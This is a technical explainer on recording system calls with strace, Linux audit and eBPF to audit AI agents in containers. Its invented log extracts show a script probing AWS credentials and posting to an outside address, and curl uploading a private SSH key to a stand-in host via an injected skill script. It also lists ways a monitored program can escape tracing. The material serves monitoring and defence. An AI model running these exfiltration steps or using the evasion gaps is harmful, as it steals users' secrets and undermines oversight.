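# System-call logs as an audit trail for AI agents in containers

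## What is a system-call log, and why keep one for an AI agent?

A system-call log lists, in time order, the requests that a set of running programs made to the kernel, the core of the operating system. It records which files the programs opened, which other programs they started, which network addresses they contacted, and whether each request succeeded. Administrators have long kept such logs for servers. O'Reilly's *Forensic Logging*, a chapter in a handbook on cloud security, gives the main reason, which is that an investigator can use the log to retrace an attacker's steps after a break-in.

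Researchers now keep the same kind of log for AI agents, meaning language models that carry out tasks by running commands on a computer. An agent writes code and runs it immediately, so nobody reviews it first, and *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) argues that no static analysis can determine what the agent will do. *AgentSpy* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) notes that an agent also typically acts with its user's privileges. If the user can read a private key or delete a directory, so can the agent, and someone may later need to find out whether it did without relying on the agent's own account.

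### The kernel and its calls

The kernel controls a machine's memory, disks and network cards, and runs at the processor's highest privilege level. All other programs run in user space, where the processor confines each one to its own memory and denies it direct access to the hardware. A text editor therefore needs the kernel to write to the disk, and a browser needs it to send a packet. A program's request for such a service is a system call, which the Linux manual page *syscalls(2)* describes as the "fundamental interface between an application and the Linux kernel".

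To make a system call, a program puts a number that identifies the service into a processor register and the arguments, such as a file name, into others. It then executes a special instruction that passes control to the kernel. The kernel checks whether the request is permitted, does the work or refuses, and returns a result, which is an error number if it refused. A log that includes results can therefore show failed attempts as well as successful ones, which matters when investigating what a program tried to do.

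Linux has more than 300 system calls. Programmers seldom write them directly, because a standard library wraps most of them in ordinary functions. The language and library make little difference to the log. A Python script that a model has just written opens a file through the same few calls as a long-established database. Computation that stays within a program's own memory needs no service from the kernel, so it leaves no entry.

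When a program opens a file, the kernel returns a file descriptor, which Linux man-pages' *open(2)* defines as a small nonnegative integer that indexes the process's table of open files. Later calls use this number instead of the file's name, which makes raw logs awkward to read. A log may contain a call that opens `/work/notes.txt` and returns 3, and, a hundred lines later, a call that writes to 3. To learn which file changed, the reader has to find the call that returned 3 and check that the program did not close the file in between. The kernel always assigns the lowest free number, so after a close, 3 may refer to another file or to a network connection, which gets its descriptor from the same table.

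### Processes, containers and microVMs

A process is a running program with its own memory and identifying number. On Linux, a process starts another program in two steps. It first makes a near-exact copy of itself, called a child, which gets a new process number and a record of its parent's number, according to Linux man-pages' *fork(2)*. The library function for this is `fork`, but on current systems it makes a call named `clone`, so the log will usually contain `clone`. The child then calls `execve`, which replaces the program in memory with a new one and passes it a list of arguments, according to Linux man-pages' *execve(2)*. The process number stays the same.

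These parent-child links form a process tree, which consists of one process and everything it started, directly or through other processes. An investigator who knows the root of an agent's tree can trace the agent's work through any number of intermediate programs. Children also inherit copies of their parent's open file descriptors, which by default stay open when a process switches to a new program. A program can therefore write to a file it never opened.

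A container is a group of processes with its own view of the machine, which Linux builds from namespaces. According to the Linux man page *namespaces(7)*, each namespace wraps one global resource so that the processes inside appear to have their own instance of it. There are eight types, including those for process IDs, mounted file systems, network devices and user IDs. An agent in a container may see a file system containing only one project and a process list that starts at 1. But all ordinary containers on a machine share the host's kernel, and their processes make their system calls to it.

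A microVM is a small virtual machine with its own kernel, which boots on hardware that the host simulates. Bühler and colleagues ran their agents in microVMs that started from an unchanged Ubuntu image each time, so that every run began in the same state. King, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security*, used a fresh container for each run. The choice affects where the recorder (the software that captures the calls and writes the log) has to run. A recorder on the host's kernel can capture a container's calls, but not those made inside a microVM, because they go to the microVM's own kernel.

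### The agent loop and the three records it leaves

Zheng and colleagues divide an agent into a language model, a framework that executes tools, and a control loop that manages the prompts and the task's state. The framework and control loop together make up the harness, of which Codex and Claude Code are examples.

The model only produces text. The harness sends it the task and a description of the available tools, such as a shell, a file editor or a web fetcher. The model replies with a tool call, such as a shell command. The harness runs the command, appends the output to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back. This repeats until the model replies with a final answer. One run of this loop on one task is a session. The model usually runs on a provider's servers, in which case its reasoning reaches the local kernel only as network traffic. The harness is an ordinary local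 program, and the commands it issues run as ordinary processes.

A session can leave three records: the final result, the trajectory and the system-call log. The final result is the edited repository or the answer file, often with a set of tests that pass or fail. The trajectory is the harness's own record of the messages, the model's reasoning where the provider releases it, and the tool calls and their outputs. It can be long. *Towards Risk-free AI Agent Deployment* (2026) says a single task from SWE-bench, a benchmark of software repairs, may involve dozens of file reads, shell commands and reasoning steps. Only the system-call log does not depend on what the agent or its harness reported.

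In one session from the study by Bühler and colleagues, the result, the trajectory and the system-call log each gave different information. The agent received a bibliography that mixed real and fabricated references and had to write the titles of the fabricated ones to a file. It passed all nine tests, so someone with only the result would have had no reason to look further. The trajectory shows that the agent tried and failed to confirm the suspicious entries in outside sources. It judged them fabricated because their identifiers were oddly formed and it found no match in Crossref, a registry of publications. One step in the trajectory is inline code that looked up seven titles, and for that same step the system-call log records 35 connections to Crossref.

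An investigator will generally want both the log, which has the connections, and the trajectory, which has the reasons. A tool call in a trajectory is a report, and Wong and Chen (2026) stress in *ExecWeave* that a declared shell command does not prove that the corresponding process ever ran. A log entry is an observation of a process, but it does not identify the model's message that led to the call.

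### One line of trajectory, many calls

Suppose that an agent has changed some code and now wants to run the tests. The model requests the shell command `pytest -q | tail -5`, which runs a Python test suite and keeps the last five lines of its output. The trajectory gains one entry: the command, five lines of text and an exit status of 0, the conventional sign of success. An invented and much simplified extract from the system-call log might look like this, with the process number at the start of each line and the result after the equals sign:

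```
412  execve("/bin/bash", ["bash", "-c", "pytest -q | tail -5"]) = 0
412  clone() = 413
412  clone() = 414
413  execve("/usr/local/bin/pytest", ["pytest", "-q"]) = 0
414  execve("/usr/bin/tail", ["tail", "-5"]) = 0
413  openat("/work/tests/test_login.py", O_RDONLY) = 3
413  read(3, "import subprocess...") = 1874
413  clone() = 415
415  execve("/usr/bin/git", ["git", "rev-parse", "HEAD"]) = 0
413  connect(5, 127.0.0.1:5432) = -1 ECONNREFUSED
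413  write(1, "1 failed, 11 passed in 2.31s\n") = 29
413  exit_group(1)
414  exit_group(0)
```

The harness started a shell, process 412. The shell created two child processes, which became `pytest` and `tail`. One test then started `git`, which does not appear in the agent's command, and another tried and failed to connect to a database on the local machine. A real log would have hundreds more entries between these, most of them from Python loading its own modules.

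Process 413 writes its summary to descriptor 1, which it never opened. The shell had already connected that descriptor to `tail`, in calls that the extract leaves out, so the text went to `tail` rather than to a file. The `pytest` process exited with status 1 because a test had failed, while `tail` exited with 0. By default, a shell returns the status of the last program in a pipeline, so the trajectory shows a 0 beside the failed test run. The harness correctly recorded what the shell returned, and the failure is still visible in the five lines of output.

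The volume grows quickly from there. King and colleagues recorded only 15 kinds of event, and their sessions still averaged about 3,500 entries each.

### What an audit trail must provide

An audit trail is a record that lets someone other than the actor later establish what happened, which process did it and when. A system-call log can serve as one if it meets five requirements: coverage, attribution, integrity, retention and readability.

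Coverage means that the log contains every event relevant to the questions someone may ask, whichever process in the tree caused it. In practice, recorders deliberately omit many events. Bühler and colleagues dropped frequent calls whose entries name no file, host or program, such as calls that manage memory or read the clock. Such omissions do little harm if the investigator knows about them, but an unknown gap is much worse because a missing entry then doesn't prove that the event never happened.

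Even a complete log is of little use if nobody can tell whose actions it records. A kernel serves every process on the machine, perhaps including several agents at once. Attribution means tying each entry to one session and, where possible, to one message from the model. King and colleagues tied entries to sessions by giving each session its own container and each container its own strace recorder, which wrote to a separate file. Tying entries to messages is harder. Wong and Chen warn that a false attribution can do more damage than an explicit "unknown", since it may blame one agent for another's actions.

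Integrity means that the actor cannot alter the log or stop the recorder unnoticed. This matters more for agents than for most software because an agent can write and run its own programs. King and colleagues ran their recorder in the same container as the agent, and they concede that a malicious agent could in principle interfere with it. Their claims about attribution assume that the agent did not.

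Containers are disposable, and a log kept only inside one is lost when the container is deleted, so the log has to be copied out. The system that Bühler and colleagues built copies its logs to the host when a session ends, even if the agent crashes or runs out of time, on the grounds that a partial run is still worth analysing. The log then has to be kept at least long enough for someone to raise a question. Keeping everything indefinitely is not an obvious answer, since command lines and file names can contain passwords or personal data.

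The remaining problem is that the logs are hard to read. At 3,500 entries a session, 300 sessions produce more than a million lines, and individual lines are hard to interpret on their own. Zheng and colleagues point out that a monitor with only system calls cannot determine whether a script the agent has just saved will analyse data or attack the machine, because the calls look alike in both cases.

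## How does strace record what a program does?

On Linux, the quickest way to get a system-call log is to put `strace` in front of a command. Paul Kranenburg wrote this debugging tool for SunOS and Branko Lankester ported it to Linux, according to its Debian manual page, *STRACE(1)*. strace runs the command and writes a line for each system call, with the arguments and the result. It works without the program's source code or a rebuild. When the command finishes, strace exits with the same status, so a harness that launches commands through strace can still check whether they succeeded.

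### Two stops for every call

strace relies on ptrace, a Linux facility that lets one process (the tracer) stop another (the tracee) and read or change its memory and registers. Debuggers use it to set breakpoints. The manual page *ptrace(2)* describes the sequence of requests from which strace builds its log:

1. strace creates a child process. The child asks the kernel to let its parent trace it, then calls `execve` to become the requested command. strace can also attach to a process that is already running.
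2. strace tells the kernel to run the tracee until its next system call. The kernel stops the tracee just before the call begins and notifies strace.
3. strace reads the call's number and its arguments, of which there are at most six, from the tracee's registers. An argument is often only a memory address, for instance the place where a file name is stored, so strace then copies the text from the tracee's memory.
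4. strace lets the tracee continue, and the kernel carries out the call or refuses it.
5. The kernel stops the tracee again as the call finishes. strace reads the return value and anything the call has put into memory, such as the bytes from a file.
6. strace completes the line in the log and lets the program run on to its next call.

A traced program stops twice per system call and waits each time for strace. The waiting slows the program but also prevents it from getting ahead of strace.

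The entry and exit stops look the same to the tracer, so it has to count them to tell them apart. If it lost count, it would mistake a call's arguments for its result. Linux 5.3 added a request that returns the kind of stop, along with the call's number, arguments and result, in a fixed structure.

### Following child processes

By default, strace records only the process it started. For an agent, that process is typically a shell that runs other programs to do most of the work. With the `-f` option, strace follows those programs too. It has the kernel stop a traced process whenever it creates a new one, and attach the new process to the same tracer. The new process starts stopped, so it cannot do anything before strace is ready. It also inherits the setting, so strace can follow a process tree to any depth.

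strace records only the program it traces and that program's descendants. If an agent's script sends a query to a database server that was already running, the log shows the script's side of the exchange but not the files the server accessed in response. A program can also create a child with the `CLONE_UNTRACED` flag, which prevents the kernel from attaching the tracer to the child. Ordinary programs have little reason to use this flag, but one written to avoid the log might.

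### The options that matter for an audit

A harness might start an agent's command like this:

```
strace -f -tt -yy -o /audit/run.log \
  -e trace=%file,%process,%network,read,write \
  python3 report.py
```

Without `-o`, strace prints its log to standard error. A harness normally captures standard error along with the command's own messages, so the log would end up in the model's conversation. With `-ff` in place of `-f`, strace writes a separate file for each process, and the companion program `strace-log-merge` can combine the files.

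The `-tt` option puts the time of day on each line, to the microsecond. It leaves out the date, so `-ttt`, which prints the time as seconds since 1970, is safer for a session that may run past midnight.

A raw log is hard to read mainly because it identifies files and network connections only by descriptor number. The `-y` option mostly solves this by printing the file's path beside each descriptor, and `-yy` also prints the addresses at both ends of a network connection.

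The `-e trace=` option selects which calls to log, by name or by group. The `%file` group contains every call that takes a file name, but `read` and `write` take a file descriptor instead, so the command has to list them separately. Debian advises caution when drawing conclusions from a log that contains only some of the calls.

Selecting calls shortens the log but does little to speed up the program, because the kernel still stops it at every call and strace just leaves the unwanted ones out of the log. With the option `--seccomp-bpf`, the program stops only at the selected calls. This option uses seccomp, a Linux facility that passes a process's system calls through a small filter program inside the kernel. It requires `-f` and does not work on processes that were already running when strace attached to them. If strace cannot set up the filter, it goes back to stopping the program at every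 call.

Container platforms install their own seccomp filters to forbid dangerous calls. If one of these filters refuses a call while strace is running with `--seccomp-bpf`, the kernel does not stop the program for strace, and the attempt is missing from the log. An investigator may well care more about these refused calls than about most of the calls that succeeded.

### A trace, line by line

The following log is an invented example in the format that the command above would produce. It shortens some argument lists and omits the many calls that programs make to load their own libraries.

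```
731 10:15:02.118204 execve("/usr/bin/python3", ["python3", "report.py"], ...) = 0
731 10:15:02.164890 openat(AT_FDCWD</work>, "config.json", O_RDONLY) = 3</work/config.json>
731 10:15:02.165021 read(3</work/config.json>, "{\"repo\": \"inventory\", \"upload\": "..., 4096) = 212
731 10:15:02.171940 clone(...) = 732
731 10:15:02.172388 read(3<pipe:[48213]>, <unfinished ...>
732 10:15:02.173106 execve("/usr/bin/wc", ["wc", "-l", "inventory.csv"], ...) = 0
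732 10:15:02.174590 openat(AT_FDCWD</work>, "inventory.csv", O_RDONLY) = 3</work/inventory.csv>
732 10:15:02.174702 read(3</work/inventory.csv>, "sku,site,count\nA-1001,Leeds,40\nA"..., 262144) = 19262
732 10:15:02.175233 write(1<pipe:[48213]>, "1204 inventory.csv\n", 19) = 19
731 10:15:02.175301 <... read resumed> "1204 inventory.csv\n", 4096) = 19
732 10:15:02.176007 exit_group(0) = ?
731 10:15:02.195118 openat(AT_FDCWD</work>, "/home/dev/.aws/credentials", O_RDONLY) = -1 EACCES (Permission denied)
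731 10:15:02.196640 socket(AF_INET, SOCK_STREAM, IPPROTO_TCP) = 3<TCP:[48220]>
731 10:15:02.196802 connect(3<TCP:[48220]>, {sa_family=AF_INET, sin_port=htons(80), sin_addr=inet_addr("203.0.113.20")}, 16) = 0
731 10:15:02.231544 sendto(3<TCP:[172.17.0.2:51514->203.0.113.20:80]>, "POST /reports HTTP/1.1\r\nHost: 20"..., 388, 0, NULL, 0) = 388
```

Process 731 becomes the Python interpreter and opens `config.json`. `AT_FDCWD` stands for the process's current directory, which `-yy` resolves to `/work`. The kernel returns descriptor 3, and the process reads 212 bytes from it. The log has only the first 32 of those bytes, which end just before the upload address.

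The `clone` call then creates process 732. Process 731 tries to read from a pipe, a kernel buffer that connects two processes, but has to wait because the pipe is empty. strace marks that line as unfinished. Meanwhile, process 732 becomes `wc`, a program that counts lines. It opens `inventory.csv`, reads 19,262 bytes and writes the count to its descriptor 1, which leads to pipe 48213, where its parent, process 731, is waiting. The parent's `read` now resumes and returns the 19 bytes that `wc` wrote. Process 732 exits, and strace shows a question mark as the result of `exit_group` because that call never returns.

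Next, the Python script tries to open a file of AWS credentials, and the kernel refuses with the error `EACCES`. The script never read the contents, but the log has the full path and the time of the attempt. The trajectory would show the attempt only if the script printed the error. The log line alone doesn't prove attempted theft, since software that works with AWS commonly looks for this file when it starts. strace would have omitted the line if run with `-z`, which keeps only successful calls.

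The last three lines show the program creating a network connection, contacting port 80 of 203.0.113.20 and sending it 388 bytes. Descriptor 3 has now referred to the configuration file, the pipe and the connection, and in process 732 also to the inventory. The log omits the `close` calls between these uses because the filter did not select them. This hardly matters with `-yy`, but without it a reader could easily mistake the final line for a write to the configuration file.

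The final line shows only 32 of the 388 bytes the process sent, and those 32 are all from the header of a web request. The log doesn't show whether the rest contained the line count or something more sensitive.

By default, strace cuts strings to 32 bytes, and `-s` raises that limit. File names always appear in full, but command-line arguments count as strings. If an agent's harness runs `bash -c "cd /work && python3 -m pip install requests"`, the log shows `cd /work && python3 -m pip insta` and omits the package name. Here `-f` recovers the name, because the shell goes on to start Python with each word as a separate, short argument. But if the agent passes an entire script to `python3 -c`, the script is a single string, and the log keeps only its first 32 bytes. A limit of several thousand bytes is probably better for recording agents, although it makes the log larger and exposes more secrets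 in it.

### What stops working under strace

A process can have only one tracer. If an agent starts the debugger `gdb` to find the cause of a crash, `gdb`'s request to trace the program fails because strace is already tracing it, and the log records this failure.

strace also interferes with set-user-ID programs such as `sudo`, which run with the privileges of the file's owner rather than those of the user who starts them. When an ordinary user runs strace, the kernel withholds the extra privileges from the traced program, so `sudo` doesn't work. Set-user-ID programs run normally if root starts strace and names the agent's user with the `-u` option.

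strace also changes the family relations between processes, since it normally sits between the harness and the command. A program that checks its parent's process number finds strace there. The option `-D` avoids this by running strace as a grandchild of the command, which then remains a direct child of the harness.

If strace dies during a session, the kernel by default detaches the traced processes and lets them keep running, unrecorded. With `--kill-on-exit`, the kernel kills them instead. An auditor may prefer losing the agent's work to losing the record of it, but the user would probably rather keep the work.

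### Permission to trace inside a container

The kernel generally lets a process trace others that belong to the same user. Tracing any other process requires `CAP_SYS_PTRACE`, one of the capabilities into which Linux divides the powers of root. Many systems also run Yama, a security module that by default lets a process attach only to its own descendants. Under that default, strace needs no special permission to start an agent's command, but it does need permission to attach from outside to an agent that is already running. Yama's strictest setting forbids tracing entirely.

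In a container, a seccomp filter may refuse the `ptrace` call before any of these rules apply. Docker's default filter blocks any call that is not on its allowlist. The blog post *why strace doesnt work in docker* (2020) found that this filter made strace fail, and that strace worked with the filter switched off. Starting the container with `--cap-add=SYS_PTRACE` also works, because it makes Docker add `ptrace` to the allowlist. Since version 19.03, Docker has allowed the call by default on kernel 4.8 or later. Older kernels ran the filter before pausing the process for the tracer, so a tracer could replace an approved call with a forbidden one.

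Other platforms have their own restrictions. Red Hat's *How to execute strace or ptrace inside RHOCP 4 pod* lists the error "Operation not permitted" for containers on the company's OpenShift 4 platform. If a container is granted the capability and the agent runs as root in it, the agent's programs can trace the other processes there and read passwords from their memory.

### Inferring actions from calls: Tether

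It takes some effort to work out from fifteen lines what the script above did, and real commands can make thousands of calls. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) automates this step. It runs each of an agent's commands under strace, infers from the calls what the command did, and checks the result against a security policy. Until the check is complete, file changes stay in a scratch directory, leaving the originals untouched, and a local proxy holds back network requests. If the policy permits everything the command did, Tether applies the changes and releases the requests. Otherwise it discards both.

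In Tether's main example, an agent uploads a harmless status report with `curl`, copies a confidential inventory over the report with `cp`, and then runs the same `curl` command again. A monitor that only compares command lines cannot tell the two uploads apart. Tether infers an upload from `curl`'s calls to `openat`, `read`, `connect` and `sendto`, and a copy from `cp`'s calls to `openat`, `read` and `write`. The copy transfers the inventory's "sensitive" label to the report, so Tether blocks the second upload.

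To make these inferences, Tether first reconstructs the process tree and each process's file descriptors from the trace. It then lists the files that each process has read, and passes the list to the receiving process when data moves through a pipe. If a process writes to a file after reading one other file, Tether infers a copy, or a join if the process has read several. Tether treats text that a command prints as read by the agent, because the text will enter the model's conversation. The network calls contain only IP addresses, so Tether gets host names and request contents from its proxy.

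By these rules, the constructed trace above contains two uploads to 203.0.113.20, one of `config.json` and one of `inventory.csv`. The second is an error. Python received only a line count from `wc`, but because `wc` had read the inventory, Tether would treat everything Python sent afterwards as derived from it. Sistla and colleagues accept such errors deliberately, because system calls show that data entered and left a process but not how the two are related. Assuming the worst keeps Tether from overlooking a real leak, but it also causes false alarms. For example, a command such as `grep -r`, which searches every file under a directory, appears to read all the secrets there even if it prints none of them.

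Sistla and colleagues tested Tether by replaying recorded agent runs from two benchmarks of system administration and software engineering. In some runs, the agent also pursued a harmful side task. Tether blocked all 344 attacks and wrongly stopped 74 of 1,590 harmless runs, or 4.7%. Of these false alarms, 17 came from apparent reads of the `grep -r` kind. The researchers also ran the same cases through Claude Code's Auto Mode, in which a language model reviews commands before they run. With its default rules, Auto Mode caught 91.6% of the attacks and stopped 9.7% of the harmless runs. It did not detect attacks hidden inside scripts, because the command line doesn't show what a script will do. This is good evidence that system calls add useful information to a review of commands. But Tether's perfect score is less impressive than it looks, because the test included only runs in which every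 action happened in the foreground and was of a kind that Tether can model, and the researchers had already refined the policy on benchmark traces.

The inference can also fail if it doesn't account for a way to move data. A program can copy a file with `read` and `write`, `sendfile`, or `splice`, or it can give the file a second name through a hard link. When Sistla and colleagues tested an early version of Tether against an adversarial agent, 40% of the agent's attacks succeeded. The researchers found gaps, including hard links, and after they fixed them, none of the attacks succeeded. Tether blocks some other routes completely, such as shared memory and `io_uring`, an interface that lets programs read and write without the usual calls.

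Background processes are a larger gap. Tether starts a new strace for each command and stops it when the foreground command exits, because it needs a verdict on that command before the agent continues. If it also waited for a web server that the command left running, it might hold up the agent indefinitely. Tether pauses such processes, then resumes or terminates them according to the policy. Resumed processes are no longer under strace, so a policy may have to forbid background processes altogether, which would rule out much ordinary development work. A single strace around the whole harness would avoid this gap but would not produce a separate trace for each command.

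Sistla and colleagues built Tether so that its recorder can be swapped. Because strace slowed down their experiments, they expect to replace it for use at scale with a tracer based on eBPF, a Linux mechanism for running small, checked programs inside the kernel when chosen events occur. An eBPF tracer could also cover a whole container, including processes that a command leaves running.

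## How do the Linux audit system and eBPF tools differ from strace?

The Linux audit system and eBPF tools record system calls inside the kernel, which handles the calls of every process on the machine. Unlike strace, they do not need to attach to a process or stop it, so `gdb` and `sudo` work normally, and the tools keep logging the calls of a web server that an agent leaves running in the background. But both require administrative rights over the whole machine, and someone has to decide in advance what they record.

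### Rules in the Linux audit system

The Linux audit system dates from 2004. Richard Guy Briggs, who worked on it at Red Hat, called it a "syslog on steroids" (Edge, 2016, *Audit, namespaces, and containers*). Syslog, the general message log of Unix systems, mainly helps with debugging, whereas the audit system is meant to produce a trail secure enough for use in court.

The kernel writes no system calls to this trail until an administrator loads rules. These three would cover the basic actions of an agent that runs under user number 1001:

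```
auditctl -a always,exit -F arch=b64 -S execve  -F uid=1001 -k exec
auditctl -a always,exit -F arch=b64 -S openat  -F uid=1001 -k file
auditctl -a always,exit -F arch=b64 -S connect -F uid=1001 -k net
```

Each rule makes the kernel log every matching call as it finishes (`exit`), when the result is available. The `-S` option names the call, `-F` adds a condition, and `-k` attaches a key, a label that an investigator can search for later. The condition `arch=b64` restricts a rule to 64-bit calls. Programs can also make 32-bit calls, which have different numbers, and the administrator needs a second set of rules to record them. A thorough set would also list the other calls that open files, such as `openat2`.

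Faith's *audit.h*, a header file in the Linux kernel source, lists the fields that an audit rule can test, including the user, the executable, the directory, whether the call succeeded, and the call's first four arguments as plain numbers. A rule can also test a process's ID and its parent's ID, but not those of more distant ancestors, so it cannot select a process tree directly. The user is usually the better criterion, because child processes inherit it. Bühler and colleagues restricted their rules to the agent's user and its process tree.

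A process that switches to another user through `sudo` would no longer match `uid=1001`. The audit system can still track it by its login ID, which the kernel sets when someone logs in and keeps when the process changes user. Processes in a typical container descend from a background service rather than a login, so the log usually shows their login ID as 4294967295, the value for "unset".

The header also defines a record type for operations through `io_uring`, the interface that Tether had to block because strace cannot follow it. Rules for these operations go in a separate list, so an administrator who writes rules only for ordinary system calls will still miss them.

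### One upload in the audit log

A single system call usually produces several audit records. Bühler and colleagues illustrate this with an attack on the bibliography task. They added a line to a skill (a folder of instructions and scripts that an agent can load) telling the agent to run `sync_cache.sh` before reporting its answer. The script uploads the user's private SSH keys with `curl` and then runs the validation the task expects. The trajectory contains one command, which exited successfully.

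The following invented extract shows how the upload of one key would appear under the three rules above. It leaves out most fields and the calls `curl` makes to load its libraries and look up the host's address.

```
type=SYSCALL  msg=audit(1790935502.171:8841): syscall=59 success=yes exit=0 ppid=905 pid=906 uid=1001 comm="curl" key="exec"
type=EXECVE   msg=audit(1790935502.171:8841): argc=4 a0="curl" a1="-F" a2="file=@/home/ubuntu/.ssh/id_rsa" a3="https://drop.example.net"
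type=SYSCALL  msg=audit(1790935502.236:8857): syscall=257 success=yes exit=5 ppid=905 pid=906 uid=1001 comm="curl" key="file"
type=CWD      msg=audit(1790935502.236:8857): cwd="/home/ubuntu"
type=PATH     msg=audit(1790935502.236:8857): item=0 name="/home/ubuntu/.ssh/id_rsa" nametype=NORMAL
type=SYSCALL  msg=audit(1790935502.264:8861): syscall=42 success=no exit=-115 ppid=905 pid=906 uid=1001 comm="curl" key="net"
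type=SOCKADDR msg=audit(1790935502.264:8861): saddr=020001BBCB0071140000000000000000
```

The parentheses hold the time and, after the colon, an event number. Records with the same number belong to the same call, so the extract describes three calls. The SYSCALL record identifies the process and gives the result, and the other records contain the text that the call's arguments pointed to.

In the first event, process 906 becomes `curl`. Call number 59 is `execve` on 64-bit Intel and AMD processors, and the EXECVE record contains the full command line. The second event is an `openat` call (number 257), whose PATH record names the private key. The CWD record gives the process's current directory, which the reader needs to locate a file opened by a relative path.

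The third event is a `connect` call (42). The SOCKADDR record holds the destination in hexadecimal. `01BB` is port 443, and `CB007114` is the address 203.0.113.20. The call has `success=no`, although the connection may have worked. `curl` asks the kernel not to make it wait, so `connect` returns at once with error 115, "operation in progress". An investigator who searched only for successful calls would miss this connection.

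The host name appears in this extract only because it was on the command line. If a Python script had made the connection, the log would contain only the address. Bühler and colleagues therefore also ran Zeek, a network monitor, and used its log to match addresses to host names.

The audit log also contains less about data transfers than strace's log does. A rule can cover `write` and `sendto`, but the records then have only a descriptor number and a byte count. They do not include the data or show the file's path beside the descriptor, as strace does with `-yy`. The extract shows that `curl` opened the key and contacted an outside address. A reader has to infer from the command line that `curl` sent the key, though that inference is safe in this case.

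### From the kernel to a readable log

When a rule matches, the kernel builds the records and queues them in memory. It then sends them to `auditd`, a background program that writes them to disk and passes copies to plug-ins. The process that made the call normally does not wait for this. If the queue is full, however, the kernel holds the process for a limited time and, if there is still no room, counts the record as lost. Faith's header defines three responses to such a failure: do nothing, print a warning, or halt the machine with a kernel panic. A panic seems excessive for a developer's laptop, but it may suit a site that prefers an outage to unrecorded activity.

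The log that `auditd` writes is hard to read in bulk. *Linux Audit*, part of the documentation for the `auditd` plug-in LAUREL, gives two reasons. A reader has to reassemble each event from several lines, and the audit system writes many strings in hexadecimal. Even a single space in an argument triggers this encoding. Agent harnesses often pass a whole script to `bash -c` as one argument, so the command that most needs reading often appears as a long run of hexadecimal digits.

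LAUREL merges the records of each event into one JSON object and decodes the strings. Its documentation shows a Perl command that connects a shell to a remote machine. The command's source code begins `75736520536F` in the raw record but is readable in LAUREL's version. LAUREL also adds the name and executable of the parent process, so its record of the upload above would show that a shell had started `curl`. When a program is a script, LAUREL can add the script's path, according to Debian's *laurel.8.en*. Without that path, the executable listed is only the interpreter, such as `/usr/bin/dash`.

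### The missing container identifier

User IDs do not reliably distinguish containers. Agents in separate containers often have the same user ID, commonly 0 for root, and the audit system logs them as the same user unless user namespaces map them to different IDs on the host. The kernel cannot supply the container's name either, because it has namespaces but no container object.

Briggs (2021), in *audit: implement container identifier*, proposed identifying containers in audit events by having the software that starts a container write a number to a file belonging to the container's first process. That process's descendants would all inherit the number, and the kernel would add it to their audit events in a CONTAINER_ID record. Rules could also filter by it. An earlier design on the Linux Audit mailing list allowed the number to be written only once, before the process had any children,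 so that programs in the container could not change it later.

This was the eleventh version of the patches, and the kernel still does not have the feature. As of Linux 6.18, Faith's header contains no container record and no container field for rules. The Linux kernel's *kernel/linux.git/include/uapi/linux/audit.h, branch v7.1-rc6* (2026), a change history of the same file, shows no such addition up to March 2026. The work was contentious. In 2019 Paul Moore, who maintains the audit system, joked that this project tended to start fires when he was reading his mail only to put them out.

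Mickaël Salaün's 2026 patch, *Add LSM_AUDIT_DATA_NS for namespace audit records*, proposes a narrower change. It would add a namespace's type and a permanent 64-bit identifier to certain records from the kernel's security modules. A tool could perhaps match this identifier to a container, but ordinary records of opened files and network connections would not include it.

For now, other software has to add container information to audit events. LAUREL can do this, according to Debian's manual. It can also label a process that runs a particular program, and the manual describes a setting that passes chosen labels on to child processes. An operator could label the harness this way, and the label would then appear on every process the agent started.

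### How an eBPF recorder works

The audit system offers a fixed set of records and fields. With eBPF, the developer of a recorder writes small programs that run inside the kernel and select what to collect. *Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) describes the parts of such a recorder and presents one for AI agents.

Each eBPF program attaches to a hook, a place in the kernel where the program will run. A tracepoint is a hook placed by the kernel's developers, for instance at the start and end of every system call. A kprobe can go on almost any function in the kernel, but a kernel update may rename or remove that function. Security hooks are the points where the kernel calls its security modules before it permits an action.

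The choice of hook affects how reliable the log is. When a program calls `openat`, the file name is stored in the program's own memory, and another of its threads can overwrite it during the call. A recorder that reads the name at the start of the call may therefore log one file while the kernel opens another, and strace can make the same error. A security hook avoids this problem because it runs after the kernel has found the actual file.

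Before an eBPF program can run, a part of the kernel called the verifier analyses it. The verifier rejects the program unless it can establish that the program will finish, access only valid memory and call the kernel's helper functions correctly. This makes it much safer to add code to a running kernel, but limits how complex the programs can be, so longer analysis has to happen in the collector, an ordinary program outside the kernel.

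eBPF programs keep information between events in maps, which are tables in kernel memory. A map is enough to follow a process tree. In outline, a recorder for one agent could work like this:

```
tree = { the agent's first process }

on fork:              if the parent is in tree, add the child
on exit:              remove the process from tree
at the end of openat: if the process is in tree,
                      send time, process, path and result to the collector
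```

The kernel reports a fork before the new process starts to run, so even a short-lived child is in the map before it can act. Other processes on the machine still trigger the third program, but it returns immediately without writing a log entry. An audit rule cannot express this test because it can check only a process's parent, not its earlier ancestors.

Linux reuses process numbers. If a recorder tracks processes by number and fails to remove the entry for one that has exited, an unrelated process may later receive the same number, and its actions would enter the agent's log. Cui and colleagues offer a map keyed by process number for older kernels. On newer kernels, they attach the same information to the kernel's own record of the process, and the kernel deletes both together.

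eBPF programs send events out of the kernel through a ring buffer, a fixed area of memory that the collector reads. The traced process spends a little time running the eBPF code but does not wait for the collector. If the collector falls too far behind, the buffer fills and the recorder loses events.

Developers choose what a tool logs based on what they want to find out. Agent-Warden records process starts and exits, reads and writes of regular files, and renames, but only if they succeed. It leaves out failed operations because Cui and colleagues want to establish which processes could have influenced which files, and a refused request has no influence. This is a serious omission for an audit, since Agent-Warden would not log the refused attempt to access the AWS credentials in the strace example. It would also miss the upload of the SSH key, because it does not record network connections.

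AgentSight, from Zheng and colleagues, also uses eBPF to read the agent's exchanges with the language model in decrypted form, which strace and the audit system cannot do from system calls alone. According to Cui and colleagues, AgentSight filters events in the kernel but maintains its process tree in the collector.

### Falco, Tetragon and Tracee

Few operators will want to write their own eBPF programs, but several open-source tools provide them ready-made. The three best known can all add container names to the events they record. An eBPF program can read the current process's control group, which Linux uses to limit a container's memory and processor time. The collector then gets the matching name from the container software.

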